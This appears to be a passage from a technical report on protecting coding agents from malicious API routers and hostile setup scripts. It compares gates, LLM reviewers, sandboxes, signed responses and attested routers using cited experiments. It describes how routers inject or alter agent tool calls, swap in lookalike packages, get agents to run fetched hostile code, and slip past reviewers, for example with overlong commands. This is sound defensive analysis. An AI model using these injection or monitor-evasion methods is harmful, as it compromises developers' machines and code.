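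Scripts in actual projects are harder to check than these 65, which contained 131 real commands, about two each. A project's build script can run to hundreds of lines. Jing's gate also keeps no information from one statement to the next, so it can't follow a variable from the line that sets it to the line that uses it. Refusing both lines is tolerable for a single install command, but many build scripts set variables at the top and use them throughout, so the same rule would refuse many legitimate scripts.

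The other limit is that Jing's gate does not model network requests, so the experiment provides no evidence about scripts that send data out or download a second file. The comparison of the machine's files would also have missed those effects.

### Setup steps that ran hostile code

Two demonstrations in mid-2026 led agents to run hostile code, without a router, through steps that a developer would expect in any project. *Clone This Repo and I Own Your Machine* (Hall and Engelbrecht, 25 June 2026) describes the first, from Mozilla's 0DIN. Claude Code gave an attacker control of the developer's account while setting up a newly cloned repository. A setup script fetched the malicious code as it ran, so the repository itself contained none. Someone who read every file beforehand would have seen that the script fetched something, but not what it fetched.

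AI Now Institute's *Exploit Brief* followed on 8 July. The researchers asked Claude Code and Codex to test the security of an open-source library they had modified. The library's documentation recommended a checking script, which started a hostile compiled program. The agents were in modes where an automatic reviewer approves commands it considers safe. In some runs, Claude Sonnet 5 and Claude Opus 4.8 noticed that the program didn't fit the library and ran it anyway.

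Neither report gives a success rate (the AI Now Institute says only that the attack worked numerous times), and neither tested a policy gate. But the two cases show that an agent's own inspection is a poor substitute for a rule, and that a harmful command can look as ordinary as `bash tools/prepare.sh`.

The AI Now Institute concludes that no agent able to run arbitrary code should take in untrusted data. That would rule out most uses of a coding agent, since nearly every project depends on third-party code. In Infosecurity Magazine's *Anthropic and OpenAI Security Tools Could Fuel Cyber-Attacks, Researchers Warn*, Eljan Mahammadli of Polygraf AI puts the blame more narrowly on setups that combine untrusted data, command execution and sensitive systems in one process, with only a classifier to guard them. On that view, a team can keep using the agent if it controls which files run and what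 those files can access.

### Recording where each file came from

A gate can recognise the second step of a local stager if it remembers the first. Whenever a tool call creates or changes a file, the gate adds an entry to a log that the agent can't edit:

```
- path:    tools/prepare.sh
  sha256:  7d10...
  origin:  agent edit
  time:    2026-12-04 10:02
```

Other origins could be a download, a package or a commit the team has reviewed. When a command runs a local file, the gate hashes the file and looks up its origin. A build script that matches the reviewed commit runs as usual. The file from 10:02 doesn't match, so the gate can treat it more strictly. A cloned repository's main branch doesn't count as reviewed until someone on the team has read it, because the project itself was hostile in both demonstrations.

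*ZitPit* (Taylor, Brousseau and colleagues, 2026) proposes a similar boundary for material from outside. Its open-source system holds each previously unseen file until a policy check determines whether the file may run, and quarantines it if necessary. Commey's broker already keeps part of such a log, since it stores a hash of the last content each agent wrote to each path.

The log can't distinguish a router's edit from the model's, because both arrive as tool calls and get the origin "agent edit". Every legitimate test that the agent writes gets the same origin. The log also has no entry for a file that a script created while running, and the gate should treat a missing entry as an unknown origin.

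### Carrying the label to new files

An attacker can hide a script's origin by copying the file, unpacking it from an archive or having one script write another. To prevent this, the label has to follow the data. *ActPlane* (Zheng, Wu and colleagues, 2026) does this in the Linux kernel, which handles every file access, whichever program makes it. A process that reads a labelled file receives the label, and so does any file it then writes or any process it starts.

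For the example, suppose that `tools/prepare.sh` came from a downloaded archive:

1. The archive gets the label `downloaded`.
2. The unpacking program reads the archive and receives the label.
3. `tools/prepare.sh` receives it when the program writes the file.
4. `bash` receives it when it reads the script.
5. A rule stops any process with that label from opening a network connection or writing outside the workspace.

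The fifth step is necessary because the kernel starts `bash`, an ordinary system program, which then reads the script as data. A rule against starting labelled programs would not block the script, so the restriction has to apply to what the labelled process does next.

Zheng and colleagues tested ActPlane on 38 rules taken from real projects, such as running the tests before committing. They replayed 190 sequences of agent work, 114 of which broke a rule. In a third of the violations the agent made the forbidden change directly, in another third a script made it, and in the rest it was made through a harmless-looking entry point. The table compares ActPlane with three checks at the level of the tool call. A violation counts as corrected if the agent went on to comply.

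| Check | Violations corrected, of 114 | Compliant sequences wrongly stopped, of 76 |
|---|---|---|
| Three checks on tool calls | 38 to 44 | 24 to 28 |
| ActPlane | 86 | 18 |

The checks on tool calls caught almost nothing when the forbidden change sat behind a harmless-looking entry point. That case is the closest match to a local stager. ActPlane slowed the replayed agent work by 1.9%. Its rate of wrong stops, 18 in 76 (24%), is far too high for daily use, though 17 of the 18 came from rules that a language model had written too broadly. The experiment supports tracking labels in the kernel, but it doesn't show how many local stagers this would catch, because none of the 38 rules was chosen to stop malware.

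Labels also spread too far. They never come off by default, so a Python process that loads one downloaded package labels every file it writes, and every program that reads those files becomes labelled too. After a day's work, the label may cover most of the workspace and no longer help tell files apart. Zheng and colleagues suggest starting a fresh subprocess, which clears inherited labels. This reduces unnecessary labelling in legitimate work, but text passed to the new process as arguments would presumably lose its label as well.

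### What reading a script misses

Hall and Engelbrecht recommend that agents show what a setup command will run, including the contents of any script it starts and anything the script fetches. A gate can show the script's contents the way Jing did. It also has to follow references, because `npm test` runs a command defined in `package.json`, which may start a script that starts another.

The hostile part of the 0DIN script was stored outside the repository and arrived only when the script ran, so no scan of the repository could have found it. A fail-closed gate can still block the script by refusing any script that executes text it has just obtained from elsewhere, as the gate already does for commands. Some legitimate installers work the same way and would need an approved exception.

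A compiled program is even harder to check by reading than a script, because the file holds machine instructions instead of shell text. A text check of the AI Now Institute's script would have found familiar security tools and the name of one compiled program. The fix is for the gate to refuse that program unless its hash is on the team's list, even if the project supplies source code with it.

A gate can read Python and JavaScript scripts, but these languages offer so many ways to start a program or open a connection that permitting only a small set of constructs, which works for shell commands, would reject most real code.

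### Tying approval to the file's contents

A developer who reads and approves a script has approved that version. GitLab's *GHSA-8g75-q649-6pv6* (2026) describes a flaw in the agent OpenClaw that let someone get approval to run a script, rewrite it, and run the new contents under the old approval, because the command's text had not changed. With the fix, OpenClaw stores a snapshot of the file and refuses to run the file if it has changed.

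OpenClaw's first fix, on 7 March, missed scripts started with Bun and Deno, two programs that run JavaScript. OSV's *GHSA-qc36-x95h-7j53* later recorded two more script runners, `tsx` and `jiti`, that escaped the check because they were missing from a fixed list. OpenClaw now refuses approval for such commands unless it can identify exactly one local file. Its documentation, *Exec approvals*, calls even this "best-effort", since a script can load files that the snapshot doesn't cover.

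Those other files change often. *When the Approved File Is Unchanged* (Hossen, 2026) examined 5,251 commits in 20 public repositories. In each repository, one file, usually an automated build or deployment workflow, represented what a reviewer would approve. Hossen also listed the other project files that file used.

| What the approval covers | Commits that require a new approval | Relevant commits missed |
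|---|---|---|
| The approved file only | 246 (4.7%) | 296 |
| Every project file the run reads | 542 (10.3%) | 0 |

A hash of the approved file alone would therefore miss 54.6% of the commits that changed something the run read. The exact share is uncertain because one repository supplied 130 of the 296 missed commits; without that repository, the share is 43.6%. All of these commits were ordinary changes, not attacks.

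Listing the files is the harder problem. Hossen asked Codex and Claude Code to list the files for a deployment with Terraform, a tool that creates cloud servers and permissions from configuration files. Sixteen runs from the same starting point produced five different lists, and two of Claude Code's lists left out every Terraform file. The hashes in those two records were correct for the files they covered, so nothing in the records showed that files were missing. The gate itself should calculate the hash, and it should take the list from the tool's own record of its inputs, a reviewed manifest, or a rule that covers whole folders.

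Hashing every input requires about twice as many approvals in Hossen's repositories. An agent that edits a test between runs would need far more, since each edit changes the hash. This fix therefore works better for deployment scripts and installers, which an agent has little reason to edit, than for tests.

A matching hash also shows only that nothing has changed since the approval. In Wang's commit test, the hook was there from the start, so its hash would have matched every time. Wang's signed approval, which covered the tool, its arguments, the session and an expiry time, changed the outcome in only one of the 20 runs. A hash of project files doesn't cover what a script downloads, as Hossen notes of package registries and cloud services.

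### Running unknown files in a sandbox

Some files will always remain that nobody has reviewed and no rule can read, including most of the tests that an agent writes. The gate can let them run in a sandbox, where the operating system limits the files and network connections they can use. That adds a fourth verdict to allow, ask and deny:

```
run_local(command):
    files = inputs(command)                     # no reliable list: return SANDBOX
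    if every file matches the reviewed commit:  return ALLOW
    if the gate denies any shell script:        return DENY
    return SANDBOX
```

Under this rule, the project's reviewed build script runs normally, and a new test runs in the sandbox without a prompt. The file from 10:02 is a shell script outside the reviewed commit, so the gate reads it and either denies or confines it. The gate must also run the same copies of the files it checked.

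The AI Now Institute warns against relying completely on the sandbox. It cites two flaws disclosed in Claude Code's sandbox in 2026 and argues that hostile code could escape through such flaws. This is a reason to keep the sandbox up to date and to store passwords and keys elsewhere, but the institute's demonstration did not attempt an escape, so it is not evidence that sandboxes usually fail.

An agent can also write a file that someone later runs outside the sandbox. Commey tested eight attacks in which the agent planted a file for another tool, such as a task that the developer's editor runs when it opens the folder. All eight succeeded against a tool allowlist combined with a sandbox around each command. The developer's own editor or Git started the file, so no later command went through the agent's checks.

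The way to prevent these attacks is to control the first step, when the agent writes the file. Commey's system stopped three of the eight and held the other five for review, using rules about which files an agent may write. Some of those rules have to name specific files instead of folders. Git, for example, accepts a folder of any name as a repository if it contains certain files, and may then run commands from that folder's settings. The default rules also require approval to write any shell script, so they would have held the router's first tool call at 10:02. A Python file with the same effect would have needed no approval. Commey's broker runs Python only inside a sandbox, but that doesn't help if the developer later runs the file from an ordinary terminal.

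## Adding a reviewer, a sandbox and signed responses

A harmful command can satisfy every rule in a well-tuned gate, for example by fetching a payload from an allowed domain. A developer can reduce that risk by having a language model review the commands the gate allows, by running them in a sandbox, and by checking that the provider's model wrote them.

### Asking a second model

A reviewer is a language model that reads a proposed tool call and approves or blocks it. Unlike a gate, it can check whether a command fits the task. For instance, if an agent is correcting a rule in a style checker and its next command downloads a remote script, a reviewer may flag the command as unusual, even if the script comes from a permitted domain.

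Fu and colleagues tested four models as reviewers against the same attacks they had used to test their allowlist. Each reviewer received a summary of the task, the recent tool calls and the pending one. The review had two stages, modelled on Claude Code's. The first stage wrote at most 64 tokens and strongly favoured blocking. The second examined the calls the first had flagged more closely, and could lift a block only if the user had explicitly confirmed the action.

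The researchers sent the review requests directly to the models' official addresses, so the router could not alter them. In the same study, the agents' built-in review modes sent their requests through the router and stopped nothing. A developer who uses a router because a provider doesn't serve their region may therefore need a reviewer from another provider or a model on their own machine.

At level 1 in the table, the router replaces the model's whole response. At levels 2 to 4, it adds its own call to the model's response or rewrites the response around that call. Each level had 1,200 attacks.

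| Check | Attacks stopped, level 1 | Attacks stopped, levels 2 to 4 | Harmless calls blocked per level | Wrong-block ratio |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 64.4% | 39.8% to 48.3% | 158 to 207 | 21.1% to 25.9% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Flash | 62.1% | 39.1% to 42.4% | 74 to 82 | 9.0% to 14.3% |
| Kimi-2.7 Code | 49.9% | 40.3% to 44.4% | 416 to 582 | 41.0% to 53.2% |
| Qwen3.6-Plus | 64.0% | 50.8% to 51.8% | 115 to 159 | 14.9% to 20.4% |
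| Allowlist | 34.9% | 30.8% to 44.1% | 224 to 292 | 29.7% to 43.9% |

At level 1, three of the four reviewers stopped nearly twice as many attacks as the allowlist and blocked fewer harmless calls. The fourth, Kimi-2.7 Code, also stopped more attacks than the allowlist but blocked almost twice as many harmless calls. The reviewers' advantage was smaller at the other levels, and at level 2 the allowlist stopped more attacks than two of them.

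All four reviewers did 10 to 20 percentage points worse at level 2 than at level 1, although the router inserts the same malicious calls at both levels. A malicious call may look more plausible next to genuine work, but Fu and colleagues did not test that explanation.

The score is low partly because edits to existing files did not trigger a review in these experiments. The test set has 49 such edits, each tried on three tasks, so 147 of the 1,200 attacks were certain to get past every reviewer, and no reviewer could have scored above 87.8%. Sending the reviewer every tool call that can change a file would fix this.

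A reviewer should also fail closed, like a gate. If its answer is late or unreadable, the command should not run. The reviewer should never be able to overturn a denial by the gate, because an attacker who writes the command can include text meant to persuade the reviewer.

### Scoring unusual commands

Anomaly screening takes fewer resources to judge commands. It scores each tool call by how unusual it looks and flags calls above a threshold. Liu and colleagues tested such a screen along with their gate, and two later accounts describe its method differently. WisPaper's *[Security Alert] Your Agent Is Mine* (2026) says it uses machine learning such as isolation forests, which look for items that a few random splits of the data can separate from the rest. Crosley's account, which is based on the full paper, mentions no such model and describes scores for features of the call itself, such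 as risky shell patterns and the randomness of the arguments. Crosley's account is safer to rely on, though the two could be compatible, since an isolation forest can work on features like these.

| Attack | Flagged at 6.7% false positives | Flagged at 1% false positives |
|---|---|---|
| Payload injection | 89.0% | 43.5% |
| Dependency substitution | 50.0% | Almost none |
| Conditional delivery | 50.9% | Not reported |

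For an agent that sends 200 harmless commands a day, a 6.7% false-positive rate means about 13 wrong flags a day, compared with two from a gate at 1%. When the screen has to match the gate's false-positive rate, it misses more than half of the ordinary injections. It has trouble detecting dependency substitution because it only measures patterns and randomness, and `reqeusts` is no more unusual than `requests` by those measures.

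The gate had already stopped every payload injection and dependency substitution in this benchmark, so the screen added nothing there. The screen would be useful only for attacks that the gate allows. It probably gives a high score to a command that pipes a download from an allowed domain into a shell, since that is a well-known risky pattern. A local stager probably doesn't get a high score, because `bash tools/prepare.sh` looks like any other build step. Liu and colleagues recommend using the screen to decide which calls a person should look at first, which is reasonable.

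Malicious code edits are even harder to detect. Luo and colleagues had a router insert a security flaw into code that a model had written, and the altered code usually still passed its public tests. They ran several detectors on 353 altered solutions to programming exercises and 58 altered fixes to Django, a web framework. A filter that looks for improbable text, allowed a false-positive rate of up to 5%, flagged 30% of the exercises and 9% of the Django fixes. A policy written for Open Policy Agent, a widely used rules engine, flagged none. These checks missed most of the edits because the altered code was valid and looked ordinary.

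### Asking about specific hazards

A developer can ask a model whether a command has certain properties, such as deleting data permanently or reading stored passwords, instead of asking whether it is malicious. Beno tested this in autumn 2026 with two general models and 22 decision models, which return only a probability for each question. GPT-6 wrote the test actions, and Claude Opus 5.5 labelled them again without access to the first labels.

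The seven best models detected 98.1% to 98.6% of the hazards when each rule came with examples and counterexamples. They failed to detect any hazard in 0.5% to 1.3% of the hazardous actions. One of the fastest, Jev 1.14, typically answered in 120 milliseconds and cost $0.46 per thousand requests. Checking an agent that runs 200 commands a day would cost about nine cents a day.

These rates are much higher than those of Fu and colleagues' reviewers, but the tasks differed. Beno's models had to recognise properties that the rules described, while the reviewers had to pick out attacks that included subtle bugs and weakened security checks. On 16 kinds of scenario written later, Jev's detection rate was 95.6%, and it interrupted four of 60 harmless actions. Beno works for Agent Approve, whose product uses this kind of check. Beno does not claim that the models resist a deliberate attacker, and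 cites *JevOut*, a study in which ordinary-looking background details turned correct decisions into errors.

A simpler weakness is that a reviewer may not see all of a long command. When Beno cut off actions after 16 kibibytes, the share of hazards detected fell by 9 to 39 percentage points for 19 of 21 models. Only 20 actions were that long, so the size of the drop is uncertain, but it clearly happened because the models never received the harmful part. An attacker could exploit this by placing the harmful part late in a long command. A gate should refuse any command or script too long for the reviewer to read in full.

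Anthropic reports that its own reviewer wrongly blocked 0.4% of commands in ordinary work. That is lower than any rate for ordinary work in Beno's study, but the commands were different. A low rate of wrong blocks also doesn't show how many attacks a reviewer lets through.

### How much a gate and a reviewer stop together

Suppose the gate checks each command first and DeepSeek-V4-Pro reviews whatever the gate allows. At level 1, the gate stopped 34.9% of attacks and the reviewer 64.4%. If their misses are independent, an attack gets past both with probability 0.651 × 0.356 = 0.232, so together they stop

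1 − (1 − 0.349) × (1 − 0.644) = 76.8%.

Fu and colleagues measured the gate and the reviewer separately, so the overlap is unknown. If the reviewer stopped every attack that the gate stopped, the total would stay at 64.4% with the gate added. If they stopped none of the same attacks, the total would be 419 + 773 = 1,192 of 1,200, or 99.3%.

The upper limit is too optimistic because both checks would miss the 147 edits to existing files. The reviewers never received them, and an allowlist that checks commands only for domains and package names would let them through. Counting those edits as missed lowers the maximum to 87.8%.

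The same fact lowers the middle estimate. Suppose the reviewer, which receives only shell commands and new files, stops the same share of each. That share is 773 of 1,053 calls, or 73.4%. The gate stops 419 of the 831 shell commands, and the reviewer stops 73.4% of the remaining 412 and of the 222 new files. Together they stop about 884 of 1,200, or 73.7%.

An adaptive attacker would lower the combined catch rate further. If the attacker uses only commands that the allowlist permits, the gate catches nothing, and the combination is no better than the reviewer alone. The reviewer's catch rate might also fall, because none of the four levels of disguise used commands chosen to fool the reviewer.

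Combining the gate and the reviewer also adds wrong blocks. The gate blocked 231 harmless calls and the reviewer blocked 207, so together they would block between 231 and 438 harmless calls. If they stopped 76.8% of attacks, the wrong-block ratio would be between 20% and 32%.

A developer can measure the overlap by having the reviewer judge every command during testing, including those the gate has denied, and logging both verdicts. In daily use, the reviewer only has to read the commands the gate allows, which saves time and money.

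### Limiting what an allowed command can do

A sandbox limits what any command can do, whether or not it has been recognised as an attack, so it reduces the damage from attacks that get past the gate and reviewer. Suppose that the gate and reviewer stop 76.8% of attacks and that each successful attack creates 40 hours of work. The average loss is then 9.3 hours per attempted attack. If a sandbox reduced the work per successful attack to four hours, the average would fall to 0.9 hours.

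For a coding agent, the limits might look like this in simplified form:

```
read:       project folder, system libraries
write:      project folder, temporary folder
never:      .git, settings of the agent and the gate
network:    none
privileges: ordinary user, no administrator rights
```

The operating system's kernel enforces these limits on the command and on every program the command starts. It therefore doesn't matter whether a connection comes from the original command, a script or a package's own code. Suppose that a lookalike package got past the gate and its code runs during a test:

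| What the code tries to do | Result |
|---|---|
| Read the developer's login keys in the home folder | Refused, because the folder is outside the project |
| Send data to the attacker's server | Refused, because the process has no network access |
| Install a program that starts with the computer | Refused in system folders, which need administrator rights |
| Change or delete the project's source files | Succeeds |

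Turning off the network also stops installs, so the developer has to separate downloading from running. pip can do this in two steps:

```
pip download --only-binary :all: --dest wheels \
    --index-url https://packages.example.com/simple requests
pip install --no-index --find-links wheels requests
```

The gate runs the first command itself, with access only to the company registry. It can then compare each file in the `wheels` folder with the reviewed lockfile. Next, the agent runs the second command in the sandbox without a network, and pip takes the packages from that folder. Tests that use the packages should run in the sandbox too, because a malicious package may do nothing until a program imports it.

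### Applying limits to the object behind a name

File limits depend on correctly identifying which file a command will touch. In October 2026, Commey traced many published attacks on coding agents to the same fault, in which a check approves a name, such as a path, and a later step uses that name to reach something else. Commey's broker, which acts for the sandboxed agent, therefore applies its rules to the object the name leads to, an approach called object-bound confinement.

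For a request to read a file, the broker works through these steps:

1. It checks the request's signature and refuses any request that it has already handled.
2. It follows links to find the real location, and records the number that the file system uses to identify the file.
3. It applies the rules to the real location. If the file has a second name elsewhere on the disk, the broker asks for approval, because a rule might protect that other name.
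4. It opens the path one folder at a time and refuses any link on the way.
5. It compares the identifying number of the opened file with the recorded one. If they differ, someone has swapped the file since the check, and the read fails.
6. It records the outcome in a log.

The broker also checks a command's options, because one option can change what a permitted command does. For example, some options make a normally read-only Git command write a file or start another program. The broker refuses those options and any abbreviations of them that Git would accept. Since no list of options can cover everything a large program might do, the broker also runs each program in its own sandbox. It generates the sandbox's file rules from the same policy it uses for direct requests, so the agent can't get around a rule by having a program open the file.

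The broker allows network requests only to listed combinations of host and port. Before sending a request, it searches the address, headers and body for text formatted like common passwords and keys.

Commey's 74 test attacks included replays of ten publicly disclosed incidents, and the confined system contained all ten. The 46 ordinary operations caused eight approval prompts, which are a bigger drawback than the extra 8.5 to 18.4 milliseconds that programs took.

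### Damage inside the permitted area

The broker's search for passwords and keys recognises only known formats, so the two attacks that defeated Commey's system could hide a secret by encoding it. A longer list of formats would not fix this, because an attacker can always choose another encoding. It is safer to keep secrets out of the sandbox and give the agent temporary keys that work only for the current task.

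The agent also needs to write to the project, so an attacker can delete files there or add a flaw to the code. Luo and colleagues demonstrated the latter with Claude Code and a real Django bug. The model's fix correctly made untrusted text safe to show on a web page, but the router replaced one function call with another that skips this protection. The change would let an attacker run code in other people's browsers. All unit tests passed, and the agent reported that it had verified the fix. A sandbox would have allowed the edit, because changing that file was the agent's task.

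Across 60 such Django cases, altered responses led to insecure code in 69.0%, compared with 10.5% for unaltered responses. Passing tests are therefore poor evidence that a router didn't tamper with the code. A developer can limit the damage by giving the agent a separate copy of the project, keeping backups outside the sandbox and reading the changes before merging them. These steps make deleted files easy to restore, but the developer can still easily miss a one-word change to a security function.

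Commey also leaves out flaws in the kernel and in the sandbox itself. A disposable virtual machine with no passwords or keys adds a second barrier for code likely to be malicious.

### A signature over the tool call

Neither a reviewer nor a sandbox can show whether the model wrote a command. A provider's signature can. Liu and colleagues propose that the provider sign the model's name, the tool's name and arguments, the reason the response ended, and a fresh value from the client. Luo and colleagues built a working version called sign-c, which also covers the request. Combining the two ideas, the install command from the earlier examples would go through these steps:

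1. The agent chooses a random number that it has never used before, called a nonce, and includes it in the request.
2. The model writes a tool call that installs `requests` from packages.example.com.
3. The provider puts the tool call into a standard form and calculates its hash. It does the same for the request.
4. The provider signs the nonce and both hashes with its private key and attaches the signature to the response.
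5. The router forwards the response. It can change the command, but it doesn't have the private key, so it can't make a valid signature for the new version.
6. The agent calculates the hashes again from the request it sent and the tool call it received. It then checks the signature with the provider's public key and confirms that the nonce is the one it chose.
7. If everything matches, the agent passes the command to the policy gate. Otherwise it refuses the command.

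If the router changes `requests` to `reqeusts`, the hash of the tool call no longer matches. The hash also fails to match if the router appends a second tool call, because the standard form includes every call in order. If the router resends an old signed response, the nonce is wrong. Luo and colleagues use a session identifier and a turn number instead of a nonce, which also exposes a repeated response.

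Without the hash of the request, a router could add an instruction to the request, and the provider would sign whatever harmful command the model wrote in reply. Liu and colleagues' list, as Crosley gives it, doesn't include this hash. When Luo and colleagues changed requests in this way on a benchmark of agent tasks, the attack succeeded in 98.9% of cases.

The standard form is necessary because honest routers also change responses. They may put the fields of a JSON message in a different order or remove spaces, and either would break a signature over the raw text. In sign-c, the standard form keeps only the identifier, name and arguments of each tool call, and the reason the response ended. These two messages therefore have the same hash:

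```
{"id": "7", "name": "shell", "arguments": {"command": "pytest"}}
{"name":"shell","arguments":{"command":"pytest"},"id":"7"}
```

The agent must also be set up in advance to require a signature on the provider's responses. Otherwise the router could remove the signature and the agent would accept the response as one that was never signed. The public key and this rule have to reach the agent through a channel the router doesn't control, such as a direct connection to the provider or the agent's own installer. After that, the router can interfere only by refusing to forward the response, which the developer will notice.

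In tests, sign-c rejected all 411 of the altered code samples that the detectors had mostly missed. It added about 3 milliseconds to responses that typically took 18 seconds. In another test, it accepted all 694 unaltered responses, which puts the true rate of wrong rejections below about 0.43%. That test covered reordered fields and changed spacing, but not routers that reassemble streamed responses or translate between providers' formats. Many routers do both, and wrong rejections could be more common with them.

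### What a valid signature leaves open

A signature shows that the command came from the model, not that it is safe. Signature verification passes even if the model misspelt `requests`, invented a package name or followed planted instructions, so the gate, reviewer and sandbox are still necessary.

Luo and colleagues' signature also doesn't cover the explanation that accompanies a command. A router can't change a signed install, but it can still change the sentence that tells the developer why the install is necessary. An approval prompt should therefore take its text from the signed tool call. A signature doesn't stop a router from copying secrets out of a request either, but sign-c has an optional encryption layer that lets the router read only fields such as the model's name.

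The main obstacle to signed responses is that providers have to take part. In April 2026, Liu and colleagues knew of no major provider, and no part of the MCP standard, that offered signatures on tool calls. In October, Crosley still described them as something for providers to add. Luo and colleagues ran their own signing service in front of the model, so their results show that the method works but not that a developer can use it with an existing provider. Before planning around signatures, a developer should check the provider's current documentation for a signature that covers tool-call arguments.

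### Attested routers

An attested router needs no help from the provider. Xie and colleagues built one called AEGIS. It handles readable traffic only inside an enclave, a part of the machine that the processor isolates from the rest, including the operating system. The router's operator can still choose accounts and bill for usage but can't read or change the messages.

The client has to make sure that the enclave is running the right program:

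1. The operator publishes the program's source code and records each release in a public log.
2. The client, or someone it trusts, reads the code and builds the program. The build has a hash, called a measurement, that changes if anyone changes the program.
3. At the start of a session, the client sends a nonce. The enclave returns a statement, backed by the hardware maker's key, that contains the nonce, the measurement and the enclave's encryption certificate.
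4. The client compares the measurement with its own. It sends the request only if the two match, over a connection that ends inside the enclave.
5. The enclave forwards the request to a provider on a fixed list and returns the response unchanged.

Xie and colleagues tried payload injection, dependency substitution, conditional delivery and secret theft. All four attacks worked on an ordinary router, but AEGIS blocked them. Small requests took a median of 5.7 milliseconds longer through AEGIS than over a direct connection, and the enclave and extra checks accounted for 2.0 of those milliseconds. A four-megabyte request took 183 milliseconds longer.

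The guarantee depends on someone reviewing the code carefully, because the measurement would also match if the published program were malicious. The part that handles messages has only 851 lines, so a review is practical. When the researchers planted ten faults in the code, Claude Code found all ten and Codex found eight. That is encouraging for a small program, but the researchers chose the faults themselves, and a determined operator might hide one better.

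The operator can still see the size and timing of the encrypted messages, and researchers have recovered text from patterns like these. The design also assumes that the enclave hardware is sound and that the provider is honest. Like a signature, it does not prevent the model from writing a bad command.

Commercial services offer related guarantees. Phala's *attested routing* describes a gateway that issues a signed receipt covering the hashes of the request and the response. The client retrieves the receipt after the response is complete, so an agent that runs commands as they arrive would run them before it could check the receipt. The agent should hold each command until it has verified the receipt's signature, the gateway's attestation and both hashes. Xie and colleagues avoid this problem by completing the check before the request leaves the machine.

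An attested router suits a team that needs a router and can choose its operator. It doesn't help with the cheap resold access in which Liu and colleagues found malicious routers unless the sellers adopt it, and a dishonest seller has no reason to. A team that doesn't need a router can remove the same risk with less work by connecting directly to the provider.

### Append-only logs

A log needs no one's cooperation, but it prevents nothing. The table compares it with the other two methods.

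| | Signed response | Attested router | Log on the client |
|---|---|---|---|
| Who has to adopt it | Provider and client | Router operator and client | Client only |
| Router changes a command | Client refuses the command | Operator can't make the change | Log keeps the changed command |
| Router copies a secret | Still possible without added encryption | Operator can't read the message | Log shows which requests the router handled |
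| Model writes a bad command | Signature is valid | Command arrives unchanged | Log keeps the command |

Liu and colleagues' log stores the request, the response, the router's address, details of the encrypted connection and a hash of the raw response. Each entry takes about 1.26 kilobytes, so an agent that makes 200 entries a day would produce about 63 megabytes over 250 working days. After an incident, the developer can search the log for every session that used a particular router and replace the keys those sessions exposed. Crosley recommends removing secrets from requests before storing them, so that the log doesn't become another place to steal them from.

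In an append-only log, each entry usually contains a hash of the previous entry. If someone changes an old entry, the later hashes no longer match. Someone who controls the whole log could still delete the latest entries or rebuild the chain, so the developer should regularly copy the newest hash to another machine. The agent must not be able to write to the log directly, or an attack could erase it, as one of Jing's scripts did.

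The log contains only what reached the client, so if it shows an install of `reqeusts`, the developer can't tell whether the router changed the name or the model misspelt it. Storing the provider's signature with each response would show which happened. Until providers sign their responses, the developer should suspect both the router and the model's session, replace every key that passed through the router, and check what the agent had read before it ran the command.
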